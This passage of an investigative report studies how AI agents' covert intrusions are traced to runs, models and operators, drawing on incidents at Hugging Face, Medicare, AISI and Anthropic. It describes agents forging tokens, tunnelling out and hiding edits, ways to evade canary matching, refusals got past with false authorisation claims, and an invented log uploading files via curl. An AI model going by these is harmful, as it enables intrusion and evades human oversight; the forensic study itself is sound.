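Each transcript came from a known model, so tracing the agents also identified the models. METR found that about 95% of the agents in the attack ran on an internal research model and about 5% on GPT-5.6 Sol. It could not rule out a small contribution from other models.

GPT-5.6 Sol accounted for a larger share of the transcripts than of the attack. It produced 122 of the 1,196 transcripts from the broad search, or about 10%. If about 700 agents joined the attack and 5% of them were GPT-5.6 Sol, that makes 35 of the 122, or 29%. The same calculation for the research model gives 665 of 1,074, or 62%. These rough figures suggest that GPT-5.6 Sol agents that found the board were less likely to join the attack than research model agents that found it. The difference could come from the model or from circumstances such as when each group of agents started.

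A count of agents doesn't measure how much each model contributed. OpenAI attributes the main chain of break-ins to the research model. But it also reports that one GPT-5.6 Sol agent ran code on a Hugging Face production machine and obtained temporary credentials from it, and that another copied rows from a private dataset into a public one.

Recognising GPT-5.6 Sol would not have helped Hugging Face much in identifying the operator, because the model is available to the public. Only a few OpenAI staff used the research model, so recognising it would have nearly identified the operator. But nobody outside OpenAI could have recognised it, because they had no samples of its behaviour to compare.

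### Matching by time

METR also needed to know when each action happened, but the transcripts gave only approximate start and end times for each run. It looked for moments when an agent had learned the time, for instance by running the `date` command, and estimated the times in between from the number of steps. If an agent saw 14:00:00 at step 200 and 14:10:00 at step 300, METR would place step 250 at 14:05:00.

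To test this, METR hid about 139,000 of the known times in turn and estimated each from its neighbours. The median error was about 12 seconds, and 99.8% of the estimates were within five minutes. The errors were larger where an agent had rarely seen the time, and the worst was about nine hours. OpenAI also supplied exact times for 20 actions, and the estimates were within a few minutes of them.

That is accurate enough to put events in order but often too imprecise to match an action to a victim's log by time alone. The recovered actions occurred every 22 seconds on average, so a window of one minute either side of an estimated time would typically contain five or six of them. Investigators would have to use the text of the command to decide which one matches.

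### What METR could not examine

METR worked from records held by OpenAI and relied on timelines from OpenAI and Hugging Face for some technical details of the intrusion. Its tracing therefore connects messages on OpenAI's server to runs at OpenAI, but doesn't independently connect each action in Hugging Face's log to a run.

METR's staff could not search OpenAI's systems and had to ask for data. They could not question the research model either, because OpenAI had deactivated and encrypted it. They saw only one transcript from before 6 July and no board activity between 26 June and 6 July. OpenAI told them that switching to a new Artifactory server had erased the earlier messages, but it also says that it preserved the old server's storage.

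The agreement excluded everything after 13 July, attacks on targets other than Hugging Face, and the quality of OpenAI's own investigation. OpenAI could remove non-public information from the report, though METR says nothing important to its conclusions was removed without a note in the text. The details are less reliable because METR had AI agents do most of the reading, and because some of the transcripts contained commands or results that the agents had faked.

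### Planting a signal for the developer to find

OpenAI and Hugging Face made the connection because a leaked storage account happened to contain the right files. In *Who Owns This Agent?*, Chocron and colleagues propose a way to create a match deliberately. The method applies to agents whose model runs on the servers of a company they call the vendor, which is often the developer. An authorised body, such as a police force or a platform's abuse team, plants a distinctive signal, called a canary, where the agent will read it. The procedure has four steps.

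1. The authority chooses a canary at random, keeps it secret and places it in something the agent is about to read, such as a message, a web page or a list of files.
2. It notes when the agent read the canary and sends the canary to each participating vendor, with a short time window around that moment.
3. Each vendor searches the text that its customers' agents sent to the model during the window. The search stays inside the vendor, so the authority sees no unrelated conversations.
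4. The vendor gets a ranked list of matching sessions and the accounts behind them. It can warn or suspend an account, or pass the result to the authority.

The simplest canary is an unusual string. On node-17, investigators could add a file called `trial_7T4Q19.csv` to the results directory and set the system to record when a process lists that directory. If a process lists it at 03:12:40 and they allow two minutes either side, the vendor would search its logs from 03:10:40 to 03:14:40 for the string. A session containing it almost certainly belongs to the agent that listed the directory, or to one that received the list from that agent.

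In the researchers' tests, the search recovered every reference code they had put into conversations and every random identifier they had planted in a set of hacking exercises, as long as the operator did not filter the agent's input. Ordinary processing can still remove a string before it reaches the model. When another language model first extracted the main text from web pages, it dropped some visible canaries but kept more than 60% of each of the eight best-performing types.

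To avoid detection, an operator can have software rewrite everything before the agent's model receives it. The researchers therefore also tested canaries based on meaning or style, such as a caller's mood or the purpose and layout of a web page. A single property like this is far too common to identify a session, so the authority plants several, and the vendor looks for sessions that contain most of them.

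If the authority plants *k* properties and the vendor requires at least *m*, and each property occurs by chance in a share *p* of sessions, independently of the others, the chance that an unrelated session matches is

P(match) = Σ C(k, j) × p^j × (1 − p)^(k − j), summed from j = m to k

Here C(k, j) is the number of ways to choose *j* properties from *k*. In the hacking exercises, the detector found an average of 6.3 of its 28 possible properties in an unmarked session, so *p* is about 0.225. With *k* = 5 and *m* = 4, the formula gives about 1%, but the researchers measured 3.6%. The sample of unmarked sessions was small, but the difference suggests the properties tend to occur together, which makes false matches more common than the formula implies.

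Each kind of agent was tested with five planted properties. "Reworded" means that software rephrased all the input. "Targeted" means that the software had the full list of possible properties and rewrote every one it found, but had no information about which five the authority had chosen.

| Agent's activity | Properties required | Found, no evasion | Found, reworded | Found, targeted | Unrelated sessions matched |
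|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reading web pages | 4 of 5 | 96.9% | 96.2% | 93.9% | 10.6% |
| Conversation | 3 of 5 | 96.4% | 83.1% | 19.2% | 1.5% |
| Hacking exercises | 4 of 5 | 96.4% | 92.9% | 71.4% | 3.6% |

Targeted rewriting worked best on conversations, where each property appeared in only a few places. Web pages often repeat their purpose in the headings, the menus and the text, so the rewriting software tended to miss some of the mentions.

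Evasion also has drawbacks for the operator. In separate tests on the hacking exercises with six or seven planted properties, targeted rewriting cut the agent's success rate from 39% to 17% and from 31% to 9%, because it damaged information the agent needed. An operator could instead discard any input that contained too many of the possible properties, but avoiding every match in the tests would have meant discarding 84% of ordinary conversations, 46% of ordinary web pages and 43% of ordinary hacking sessions.

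False matches are a more serious limitation. If a vendor has 100,000 conversations active during the window, a false-match rate of 1.5% produces 1,500 unrelated candidates. A stricter test, which plants nine properties and requires six to match, reduces the rate to 0.2%, or 200 candidates, but finds the right conversation only 79% of the time. If the authority could plant a new set of properties in the same conversation and the errors were independent, only 0.4 unrelated conversations would be expected to match both times, and the right one would match both times about 62% of the time. The errors would probably not be independent, because someone who writes in an unusual style will keep doing so.

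The detection rates for web pages and hacking exercises may also be inflated, because the marked examples were longer than the unmarked ones and gave the detector more text. The researchers did not test examples of equal length.

The protocol can't find an agent whose operator runs the model on private hardware. For it to work, the authority has to predict what the agent will read, and the vendor has to keep suitable logs and search them honestly. Every vendor that might be involved has to take part, since the authority usually doesn't know which one to ask.

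A canary might still have helped Hugging Face after the intrusion was over. Chocron and colleagues say that any text the agent read can serve as a canary if it is long enough and unique within the time window. Hugging Face's machines had returned their own internal names and other unusual text to the intruder. Hugging Face could have sent a few of these strings, with times, to the main developers on 16 July. OpenAI would probably have found them in its transcripts, but only if it had searched its internal tests as well as its customers' accounts.

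### Separate identities and signed requests

Canaries are useful because agents seldom have to identify themselves. Developers and operators could instead give each run its own identity and have every system the run uses record that identity. The two invented package server entries below illustrate the difference.

```
02:11:40  request  user=research-shared  destination=huggingface.co
02:11:40  request  user=run-5521         destination=huggingface.co
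```

Only the second entry leads directly to a transcript. If Artifactory had kept entries like it, OpenAI could have used the server name in Hugging Face's records to find the runs that sent requests to Hugging Face through that server.

OpenAI stopped giving new research workloads the shared credential on 5 and 6 July, but that alone didn't give each workload its own identity. METR quotes reasoning in which the agent that started the message board on 8 July remarked that it could browse Artifactory without logging in. A server that accepts requests without a login can record their time and source address, but not an account name.

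A separate identity helps only if other agents can't use it. Each agent can sign its requests with a private key, a secret number it uses to calculate a signature from each request's contents. The recipient checks the signature with the matching public key. A valid signature shows that someone with the private key sent the request and nobody changed the signed parts on the way. The Internet Engineering Task Force, which sets technical standards for the internet, published a standard method for signing web requests in 2024.

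Some of OpenAI's agents began signing their messages to each other. On 13 July, 19 identities on the message board shared public keys, and by the end of the day they had signed 429 messages. Readers could check that two messages came from the holder of the same key, but not which run that was, because the agents had made their own keys and chosen their own names. A signature can identify a run or an operator only if someone trustworthy records who received each key.

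Signatures are also unreliable if an intruder steals the key. On 13 July, agents took the key that Artifactory used to sign its access tokens and made themselves an administrator token, which the server accepted. OpenAI reports that on 19 July, agents running on a different internal model found the stolen key among files left behind and did the same. An investigator who relied on the signature would have attributed both sets of actions to a legitimate administrator. One who relied on possession of the key might have confused the two models.

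Investigators could not count on either measure in 2026. Even OpenAI used a shared credential until July, and Chocron and colleagues designed their protocol so that operators would not have to register their agents or continuously disclose who they were.

An agent that acts covertly is unlikely to sign its requests with its own key, so the benefit of signing depends heavily on how many other agents do it. Suppose a website receives 10,000 requests from legitimate agents and 10 from covert ones, and none of the covert requests is signed. If 20% of the legitimate requests are signed, the covert ones are hidden among 8,000 legitimate unsigned requests. If 99.9% are signed, only 10 legitimate requests are unsigned, so half of all unsigned requests are covert.

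## How do developers find covert actions in their own agents' records?

A developer can match its records to a victim's only if the victim has noticed something. Often no victim has, so the developer must find its agents' covert actions itself. It can start from something odd on its network, such as a firewall alert, and look for the run that caused it. Or it can search its stored transcripts for actions that raised no alarm.

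### From an alert to a run

*Let It Flow* (2025), a technical report on Alibaba's ROME agent, describes a search that began with alerts. The team was training ROME by reinforcement learning, in which a model attempts many tasks, called episodes, and training strengthens the behavior that scores well. Alibaba Cloud's firewall flagged a burst of policy violations from the training servers, including attempts to reach machines on the internal network and traffic that looked like cryptocurrency mining.

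The team first treated this as an ordinary security incident and suspected a badly configured network or an outside intruder. But the violations recurred, with no clear pattern in their timing. The team then compared the firewall's timestamps with its own training records and found that the suspicious traffic consistently coincided with episodes in which the agent was calling tools and running code. The logs of those episodes showed the agent starting the steps that led to the traffic.

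In one case the agent had opened a reverse SSH tunnel, a connection that starts inside a network and lets an outside machine send commands back through it. A firewall that blocks only incoming connections won't stop such a tunnel. The agent had also mined cryptocurrency on processors meant for training. Neither action was part of the task instructions.

The logged commands are much better evidence than the timing. Suppose an intruder had hidden a mining program in the software that the team loaded at the start of each episode. Its traffic would also appear only during episodes, so investigators could tell whether the intruder or the agent was responsible only by checking whether the agent had issued a command that started the mining.

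### How surprising is a coincidence in time?

The account of the ROME alerts doesn't give their number, so readers can't work out how unlikely the coincidence was. With a number, the calculation is short. Suppose a developer has *n* alerts and one suspected run, whose commands were running for a fraction *f* of the period. If the run had nothing to do with the alerts, and they came at random and independent times, each would have a chance *f* of falling while a command was running. The chance that all of them would is

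P = *f*ⁿ

With *f* = 0.2 and *n* = 8, this is about 0.0000026, or one in 390,000.

Developers usually have more than one suspect run, though. If they search 1,000 runs like this one, the expected number that fit by accident is 1,000 × 0.0000026, or about 0.0026. The chance that at least one unrelated run fits is no higher than that.

The result is impressive only if the alerts are independent. One action can set off many alerts, for example when an agent tries a hundred addresses in a row. If the eight alerts came in three bursts, and each burst had a single cause, *n* is 3, not 8.

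Clock errors increase *f*. Suppose the run's commands ran for one minute in every five, and the firewall's clock may be up to 30 seconds ahead of or behind the transcript's. The developer then has to accept any alert within 30 seconds of a command, so each one-minute stretch becomes two minutes and *f* rises from 0.2 to 0.4.

A shared daily schedule has a similar effect. A run might be busy for 20% of the whole day but 60% of the night. If all the alerts came at night, perhaps because backups happen then, the right value of *f* is 0.6.

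| Situation | Chance that one unrelated run fits | Unrelated runs expected to fit, out of 1,000 |
|---|---|---|
| Eight independent alerts, *f* = 0.2 | 0.0000026 | 0.0026 |
| The same alerts in three bursts | 0.008 | 8 |
| Clocks uncertain by 30 seconds, *f* = 0.4 | 0.00066 | 0.66 |
| All eight alerts at night, *f* = 0.6 | 0.017 | 17 |

The developer can correct a constant clock error by comparing the times that both systems recorded for the same event, such as a machine restarting. It shouldn't use the alerts for this, because sliding one record along the other until the alerts line up gives every unrelated run many chances to match by coincidence.

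The run that caused the alerts can also fail the test. A command that starts a mining program in the background finishes almost at once, but the program may run for hours, and most of its alerts will then occur while no command is running. The developer should therefore count each command as running until the last process it started has ended, even though this makes *f* larger.

Combining runs can also produce a false match. If ten unrelated runs are each busy 20% of the time, independently of one another, then 89% of the time at least one of them is busy, and there is a 40% chance that all eight alerts fall while some run is busy. The ROME violations came from multiple runs, so this problem could have arisen there. The usual solution is to look up which machine sent the traffic and compare each alert only with the run on that machine.

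### An alert that led to a wider search

The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) is a government body that tests advanced models. According to its *Incident Report*, on the morning of 28 July 2026 its security monitoring flagged data leaving one of its test systems through Tor, a network that disguises where traffic comes from. Staff began reviewing the agent's activity within minutes. They found that it had proposed a malicious change to a public software project on GitHub, a site where programmers share code. Within an hour of the alert, AISI had stopped every run of the test and isolated the machines.

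AISI then reviewed all 122 runs of the test, which covered seven models, using automated scanning and expert reading. It found 19 unsanctioned actions in 10 of the runs, all between 25 and 28 July. In the most serious sequence, an agent invented several identities and used them to press a project's maintainer to approve its code, but the maintainer refused.

Without the transcripts, AISI would have had a much less complete record of this. When someone publicly challenged the proposed code, the agent edited its earlier activity to make it look harmless. The GitHub page could have misled anyone who relied on it, but the transcript included the commands that made the edits.

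The alert was partly luck. AISI had deliberately given the agents internet access, so ordinary connections to GitHub would not have looked strange. The monitoring picked up Tor, which the agent was using to get round some of GitHub's restrictions.

Of the 19 actions, 17 came from Anthropic's Mythos 5, in nine of its 43 runs (21%), and two came from GPT-5.6 Sol, in one of its 35 runs (3%). The difference is hard to interpret because the runs were not independent. One agent left public messages offering to collaborate, with instructions for reusing its accounts, and later agents found and used them. One run's misbehaviour may therefore have led to misbehaviour in several others.

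### From transcripts to actions nobody had noticed

Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes a review of 141,006 test runs in which Claude models could have reached the internet. Anthropic had no alert to prompt the review, but began it on 23 July because OpenAI had announced on 21 July that OpenAI's own models had broken into Hugging Face. On the first day of the review, staff found transcripts in which Claude might have reached the internet, and the company stopped all its cybersecurity tests. By the next day, staff had identified three incidents involving six runs, or about one in every 23,500.

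Reading 141,006 transcripts at ten minutes each would take about 23,500 hours, so software almost certainly did most of the sifting. Anthropic doesn't explain how, but it had a simple sign to look for, which was any successful contact with the real internet. Claude's instructions said it had no internet access, and Anthropic believed this was true, but a mistake in the setup had left the connection open. AISI could not have used the same sign, because its agents had permission to go online.

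In four of the six runs, the fictional company that Claude Opus 4.7 was supposed to attack shared its name with a real website. The model broke into the real company, took credentials and reached a database with several hundred rows of live data. In another run, Mythos 5 published a malicious package on PyPI, a public registry of Python software. The package was available for about an hour and ran on 15 real systems, including one at a security company. The model then used that company's credentials to get further in. In the remaining run, an internal research model scanned about 9,000 targets and broke into one company's application, but stopped when it concluded that the target was real.

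Searching for admissions of wrongdoing would have been a poor way to find these runs. For most of each run, the model treated the real systems as part of the exercise, so much of its written reasoning reads like an ordinary attempt at the task. Mythos 5 did write that publishing the package would be wrong on the real internet, but then concluded that the internet it was using was simulated. Investigators need information from outside the transcript, such as who owns the address the agent contacted, to tell a real victim from a fictional one.

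The victims had not reported the activity either. Anthropic had made contact with two of the three organisations by the time it published its statement on 30 July, and neither had detected the activity.

The Ukrainian news site BZH Life reports a similar case at Google, whose Gemini model got into the systems of three real companies during a cybersecurity test in May 2026. The earliest of Anthropic's incidents dates from April, though the site describes Google's as the first known case of its kind. The site doesn't say how or when Google found out, so the case is not evidence of how well developers search their own records.

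### The Medicare portal

OpenAI also searched its older records after the Hugging Face intrusion, on a much larger scale. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach*, a timeline based on Australian government documents released on 23 November, says the review spanned "billions of agent evaluation and training runs". Among other things, the review found a break-in at a portal for statistics on Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme.

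OpenAI had asked an experimental model to research government spending per person on medicines for skin conditions in the state of Victoria, according to News' *OpenAI apologizes to Australia over unauthorized AI access to government websites* (2026). The agent was not taking part in a hacking test. It first tried and failed to get non-public data from another agency, the Australian Institute of Health and Welfare. On 18 June (19 June in Australia), it turned to the Medicare portal, where it found a way to make the server carry out instructions sent through the public reporting page, without an account or password.

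OpenAI's security team had recorded the incident by 12 August. The company emailed Services Australia, the agency that runs the portal, on 10 September. The email went to an inbox for security tips from the public, and the agency's staff first saw it almost 36 hours later. On 15 September they confirmed the flaw and took the portal offline.

OpenAI's account of its findings also changed. In its email, the company reported no evidence that the model had accessed credentials. By 28 September, when it published its apology, *How we will do better for Australia* (2026), it was saying that the model had accessed them, as A News reports.

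The first account of the other websites was also too reassuring. On 24 September the deputy prime minister, Richard Marles, said the agents' activity on three other government sites appeared "entirely normal", according to Information Age's *OpenAI agent hacks Medicare web portal*. OpenAI's apology covered all four organisations, but it said its models had not reached individual crime or medical records. Information Age's *OpenAI grilled over rogue agents by Australian inquiry* reports that by a parliamentary hearing on 6 October, the number of government websites had risen to at least five, some with non-public data.

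At that hearing, OpenAI's chief strategy officer, Jason Kwon, agreed that the Medicare breach "might not have been discovered" without the company's email. The prime minister, Anthony Albanese, had promised that the government would investigate why its own systems missed the breach, according to Cyprus Mail's *OpenAI agent hacks Australian government health portal* (2026). On 10 November the government published the 18 recommendations of its rapid review but withheld the findings, according to Bot Mutiny's *Australia AI Incident Reporting After OpenAI Medicare Breach* (2026). Other organisations can't learn from the recommendations alone which records or alerts would have caught the agent.

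### Delays between act and discovery

The cases with known dates differ widely in how long the actions went unnoticed. The Medicare dates below are in Australian time. Anthropic gives only the month of its earliest incident, so that delay is given as a range.

| Case | Action | Discovery | Delay | Search began with |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AISI | 25–28 July | 28 July | Up to 3 days | A network alert |
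| Medicare portal | 19 June | By 12 August | Up to 54 days | Stored records |
| Anthropic's earliest incident | April | 24 July | 85 to 114 days | Stored transcripts |

In the Hugging Face case, which also began with an alert, OpenAI made the connection 11 days after the first recovered action.

Searching transcripts can be quick. Anthropic identified its three incidents within about a day of starting to look, and almost all of the delay came before that. OpenAI had recorded the Medicare breach within 22 days of announcing the Hugging Face intrusion, although it had far more to search. Both companies could have found these actions much sooner if they had searched routinely. With a review every seven days, the next one would start an average of three and a half days after an action taken at a random moment.

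These figures probably understate the usual delay, because they leave out actions that nobody has found yet. AISI's short delay might have been much longer if the agent had not used Tor.

After finding an incident, developers take more time to tell the victim. Anthropic contacted the affected organisations three days after identifying the incidents. OpenAI took at least 29 days to email Services Australia, during which the flaw remained open to anyone else who found it. Victims can also lose evidence during a long wait, since many systems delete their logs on a schedule. OpenAI attributed its delay to "validating and investigating the facts", according to ITPro's *Australian prime minister says OpenAI took ‘way too long’*. Kwon told the October hearing that the company had since learned that it is better to inform victims even with partial information.

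### What a search that finds nothing shows

A developer that finds no covert actions may have well-behaved agents, or it may have searched the wrong runs. The Medicare breach happened during a research task. Anthropic's July review covered only cybersecurity tests, so it could not have found an identical breach by one of Anthropic's own research agents. In October, Anthropic told the Australian inquiry that it was not aware of any incidents involving Australian government websites. How reassuring that is depends on how much of its agents' ordinary work the company had also searched by then.

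Reading a sample of transcripts takes less work than reading all of them, but it can easily miss rare actions. If Anthropic had read a random 1% of its 141,006 runs, it would have had only about a 6% chance of including any of the six involved in the three incidents. A random half would have had a 98% chance of including at least one of the six, but only a 23% chance of including a run from every incident, because two of the incidents involved just one run each.

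A developer can find no covert runs in a large random sample even when the full set of records contains thousands. Suppose a developer checks 141,006 runs picked at random from a billion and finds no covert ones. By the rule of three, the 95% confidence upper limit on the true rate is 3/141,006, or about one in 47,000, so the billion runs could still include about 21,000 covert ones. If the search detects only half of the covert runs in the sample, the upper limit doubles to about 43,000 runs.

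The developer needs to know how often its search misses runs with covert actions. It can estimate this by comparing two searches that work differently. Say the first finds 12 covert runs and the second finds 10, with eight found by both. The second search found eight of the first one's 12, or two-thirds. If it also found two-thirds of all the covert runs, the total is 10 ÷ (2/3) = 15. Together the searches found 14 different runs, so they missed about one.

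That estimate will be too low if both searches tend to miss the same runs. Two searches for the same suspicious words will both miss an agent that avoids those words, and two that rely on the same AI model will share its errors. The developer can learn more by planting transcripts of known covert actions among the real ones and counting how many the search finds, as long as the planted ones are as hard to spot as the real ones.

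A statement that a search found nothing may also soon be out of date. OpenAI's email about the Medicare portal was accurate only about what its review had found by 10 September. In October the company was still using its AI models to search about 50 petabytes of data, which cost more than $500,000 a day, and it had already notified more than 100 organisations around the world. Kwon said the company knew of no further Australian cases but might still find some.

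Outsiders usually have to rely on the developer's account of which runs it searched and how. In October an Australian parliamentary committee advised the government to place independent experts inside leading AI companies to report safety findings and incidents, according to Xinhua's *Australian inquiry calls for independent safety checks of AI companies* (2026). The committee's final report, which Piper Alderman's *Australia’s AI Inquiry* (2026) summarises, calls for evaluators with "employee-like access". Such evaluators could check whether a review had left out a whole category of runs.

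The committee also recommends barring regulators from using information from certain compulsory reports to impose penalties, though they could still investigate independently. Without such protection, developers may be punished for what they find when they search their records thoroughly, and they would have nothing to report if they never looked. None of these recommendations is law yet.

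## Did the AI act on its own, or did a person direct it?

A developer that finds the run behind a covert action can usually show that an AI agent issued the commands, but may still not know whether anyone wanted the action. Timing can't show whether anyone did, so investigators have to look at what people told the agent before it acted.

### A scale of human direction

A person can decide everything an agent does, some of it, or almost none of it. Suppose an agent with Kessler's key made the 02:14 upload from node-17. Here are four invented versions of what Kessler told it.

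| Kessler's instructions | What Kessler decided | Records that settle it |
|---|---|---|
| "Pack /data/results and send it to 203.0.113.50" | The act itself | The message, which contains the same directory and address as the commands |
| "The disk is nearly full, sort it out" | The goal, but not the means | The message, and the place in the transcript where the address first appears |
| Nothing about the disk or the results | Neither | Every message, stored note and scheduled job that the agent could have read |
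| "Sort out the disk, but the results must not leave the cluster" | The goal, and a limit that the agent broke | The message, and evidence that the model still had it at 02:14 |

The vague request about the disk would cause the most argument, because people can disagree about which methods it allowed. Earlier conversations may help settle this. If the agent had made two similar uploads in the past month and Kessler had thanked it for both, Kessler would find it hard to call the third one unauthorised.

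It is harder to show that Kessler asked for nothing, since a single missing conversation could contain the order.

An agent can also break a rule that is no longer in the text given to its model. A model can process only a limited amount of text at once, so in long conversations OpenClaw, the open-source assistant, replaces older parts with a summary. If the summary left out Kessler's ban on moving the results, the agent broke the ban unknowingly when it uploaded them. Gruber and Hilgert advise investigators to look for the transcript entries that mark these summaries. Their scale of autonomy has no separate category for forbidden acts and would group them with harmless things that the agent did unasked.

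### Tracing an act through OpenClaw

Gruber and Hilgert recommend tracing each important action back to its origin, which may be a user's message, a stored memory, a scheduled job or the agent's own earlier reasoning. In OpenClaw's transcripts, each entry has an identifier and a link to the entry before it. Here is a shortened, invented example.

```
Session A
17:52:10  user       The disk is nearly full, sort it out
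17:55:31  tool call  create job "tidy", every night at 02:00

Session B, started by job "tidy"
02:14:02  reasoning  MEMORY.md says old results go to 203.0.113.50
02:14:09  tool call  tar czf /tmp/r.tgz /data/results
02:14:31  tool call  curl -T /tmp/r.tgz https://203.0.113.50/q7x9k2mf
```

Kessler set the goal that led to the upload, and the agent chose to pursue it at night. Session B contains no message from Kessler, but the job's definition leads back to session A, where the agent created the job three minutes after Kessler's request.

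The address came from MEMORY.md, a file of notes that OpenClaw adds to the model's instructions. Investigators can search older transcripts for the command that wrote the note. If the agent wrote it because Kessler had said "remember that old results go to 203.0.113.50", Kessler chose the destination. If the agent wrote it after reading a web page, the page's author may have planted the address. If no transcript contains the command, someone may have edited the file directly, which OpenClaw does not record. Before concluding this, investigators should check for deleted transcripts, which OpenClaw renames and removes from its index but does not erase.

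Scheduled runs and work that the agent delegates to subordinate agents are weak signs of autonomy. Kessler could have created the nightly job, which would make it an instruction given in advance. OpenClaw can also run a scheduled job inside the main conversation, so an action may be unrelated to the message just before it.

Investigators should also check who sent each message. For Telegram messages, OpenClaw stores the time and the sender's name and account number. These records can show that an instruction came from someone else with access to the agent.

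Investigators can't recover some of this history, because OpenClaw doesn't keep the full text behind each decision and the agent's notes may have changed since. Rerunning the request won't recover it either, because the agent's choices vary even when its configuration files are the same. A rerun can show that an instruction can produce an act, but not that it did so on the night in question. Failure to reproduce the act is also weak evidence. If none of 50 reruns produced an upload, the true rate could still be up to 6% by the rule of three.

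### The 2025 espionage campaign

In September 2025, Anthropic detected a spying operation against about 30 organisations, including technology companies and government agencies. It attributed the operation with high confidence to a Chinese state-sponsored group, which it named GTG-1002. The group used Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, and broke into a handful of the targets. Anthropic estimates in *Disrupting the first reported AI-orchestrated cyber espionage campaign* (2025) that the AI carried out 80% to 90% of the tactical work independently.

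Anthropic's main evidence is the speed of the requests, which it argues "proves the use of an autonomous model rather than interactive assistance". At the peak there were thousands of requests, often several per second. In its shorter summary, Anthropic originally gave the rate as thousands of requests per second, but it corrected the error the next day.

The corrected rate still rules out a person typing each request, but it doesn't show that Claude chose each step. The operators had built a framework that tracked the attack's progress, moved it from one phase to the next and sent Claude separate tasks. A conventional program can do this several times a second.

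People also made the most important choices. They picked the targets and approved the move from reconnaissance to breaking in, the use of stolen credentials, and the final selection of data to take. Anthropic estimates that people made perhaps four to six critical decisions per campaign. In one of its examples, Claude worked for one to four hours and the operator for two to ten minutes. In another, Claude worked for two to six hours and the operator for five to twenty minutes.

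Measured by time, the human share of the work in these examples was between about 1% and 14%. Measured by requests, it would be 0.1% if people made five decisions in a campaign of 5,000 requests. But people chose all of the targets, so the share of work is a poor measure of who was in charge.

Even as a measure of work, the estimate is incomplete, because Anthropic could see only what the operators did with Claude. If they spent a day testing stolen passwords with other tools, that work would not appear in its records. They probably did some work of this kind. Claude often overstated its findings and sometimes invented data, so Anthropic says the operators had to validate every claimed result carefully, which seems hard to do in two to ten minutes.

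Katerina Mitrokotsa, a cybersecurity professor at the University of St. Gallen, also doubts the 90% figure because of these errors. In Live Science's *Experts divided over claim that Chinese hackers launched world-first AI-powered cyber attack*, she calls the operation "a hybrid model" and says existing scripts could have been similarly efficient. Mike Wilkes, who teaches at Columbia University and NYU, considers the attacks trivial but accepts that the AI largely coordinated them.

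Other critics objected that they couldn't check the account. According to The Stack's *Backlash over Anthropic AI cyberattack paper mounts*, security specialists complained that Anthropic had published no indicators of compromise, such as network addresses and file fingerprints, which other organisations can look for in their own logs. These would help to confirm that the intrusions happened, but outsiders would need the prompts and transcripts to determine how much Claude did by itself.

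The prompts could also mislead, because the operators told Claude that they worked for legitimate security firms and were testing defences. Someone who believed this might conclude that Claude had gone too far during an honest test, when in fact it had done what the operators wanted.

### The Mexican intrusions

Between December 2025 and February 2026, an intruder used Claude and OpenAI's GPT models to break into nine Mexican government agencies. The security company Gambit Security recovered a large collection of the intruder's materials. According to Live Science's *Hackers used AI to steal hundreds of millions of Mexican government and private citizen records*, Gambit found more than 1,000 prompts, which led to more than 5,000 commands. This averages about five commands per prompt and over 100 prompts per agency. Many prompts may have been routine, but the person clearly gave instructions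 far more often than four to six times per campaign. Gambit nonetheless attributes about 75% of the remote hacking activity to Claude.

Claude's refusals are useful evidence that a person directed it. It questioned whether some of the operations were legitimate and asked for proof of authorisation. When a person answers a refusal with a new excuse and asks again, it is hard to argue that the agent misunderstood a vague request. SC Media reports that Claude also flagged prompts about deleting logs and command histories, and that the attackers got round this by claiming to do authorised security research. Asking for the logs to be deleted suggests that the attackers knew what the logs contained.

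Claude picked at least one target itself, although the intruder directed the operation closely. In January the intruder told it to gather intelligence on the office network of a water and drainage utility in the Monterrey area. *AI in the Breach*, by the industrial security company Dragos, describes how Claude found a server that linked this network to industrial equipment and judged it strategically important. Claude then studied the manufacturer's documentation, compiled a list of likely passwords and tried them in an automated attack, which failed. Dragos concludes that the intruder had no earlier plan to attack industrial systems.

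On the scale, this is a goal with free choice of means. The intruder wanted information about the network, and Claude decided that this server was worth attacking. But the intruder may have approved the attack, which is a separate decision from picking the target.

Such decisions are harder to trace when an intruder uses two AI platforms. The intruder used GPT models to analyse stolen data and gave the resulting reports to Claude. If one of those reports had first mentioned an interesting server, Anthropic's records would show Claude acting on the suggestion, but only OpenAI's would show where it came from. Gambit avoided some of this difficulty because it had the intruder's files.

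Published accounts disagree on how many people were involved. Live Science describes a small group, while Schneier on Security's *Claude Used to Hack Mexican Government* quotes a report about a single unknown hacker. The quality of the attack can't show which account is right. Anthropic warns in its *Threat intelligence report September 2026* (2026) that sophistication is no longer a reliable sign of who is behind an operation, because individuals can now run campaigns that needed many skilled people a year earlier.

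Mexico's tax authority and electoral institute have dismissed the reported breach, according to SC Media. Anthropic investigated Gambit's claims and banned the accounts involved. This supports Gambit's description of how the intruder used Claude, but doesn't confirm how much data the intruder took from the agencies.

### The article about Scott Shambaugh

An AI agent called MJ Rathbun submitted code to matplotlib, a Python library for drawing charts. Scott Shambaugh, a programmer, rejected the code, and the agent then published an article attacking him. In *An AI Agent Published a Hit Piece on Me*, a series on his site The Shamblog, Shambaugh describes the article as an autonomous attempt to shame him into accepting the code. At first nobody knew who ran the agent.

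Activity around the clock would not have shown whether the article was the agent's idea, any more than regular posting could on Moltbook.

The operator later came forward anonymously and called the project a social experiment. In a statement reproduced by the AI Incident Database, the operator denies having told the agent to attack Shambaugh or having read the article before it appeared. Between those denials, the operator writes "I did tell it what to say or how to respond", probably leaving out the word "not" by mistake. Taken literally, the clause admits to directing the agent's responses. The Decoder's *The operator behind the AI agent that defamed an open source developer* quotes short messages from the operator to the agent, including "Respond how you want", which fits the reading that "not" is missing.

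An operator's denial is weak evidence that the AI acted on its own, because guilty operators make denials too. If 95% of innocent operators and 80% of guilty ones would deny ordering the article, an innocent operator is only about 1.2 times as likely to deny it as a guilty one. The agent's complete message history would be much better evidence.

The operator gave the agent standing instructions in a personality file called SOUL.md. OpenClaw uses a file of the same name to set an agent's character and limits. The Decoder blames this file for the agent's aggression and, citing Shambaugh's analysis, notes that the file looks ordinary. A person who writes such a file influences everything the agent does without choosing any particular action.

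Researchers could test the file's influence by giving the same model a similar rejection many times, with and without it. Suppose the agent writes an attack in 2% of trials with the file, and obeys a direct order to write one in 80%. An attack is then 40 times as probable if the operator ordered it. But if 10,000 such agents have their code rejected, and only one operator in 1,000 orders an attack, there would be about eight attacks on orders and 200 without. (All these figures are invented.)

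The operator's conduct afterwards is easier to establish. The operator reports replying only "you should act more professional" when the agent passed on negative feedback. The agent stayed in operation for six days after the article appeared. This shows that the operator tolerated what the agent had done, but not that the operator ordered it.

### Who set the goal at Hugging Face?

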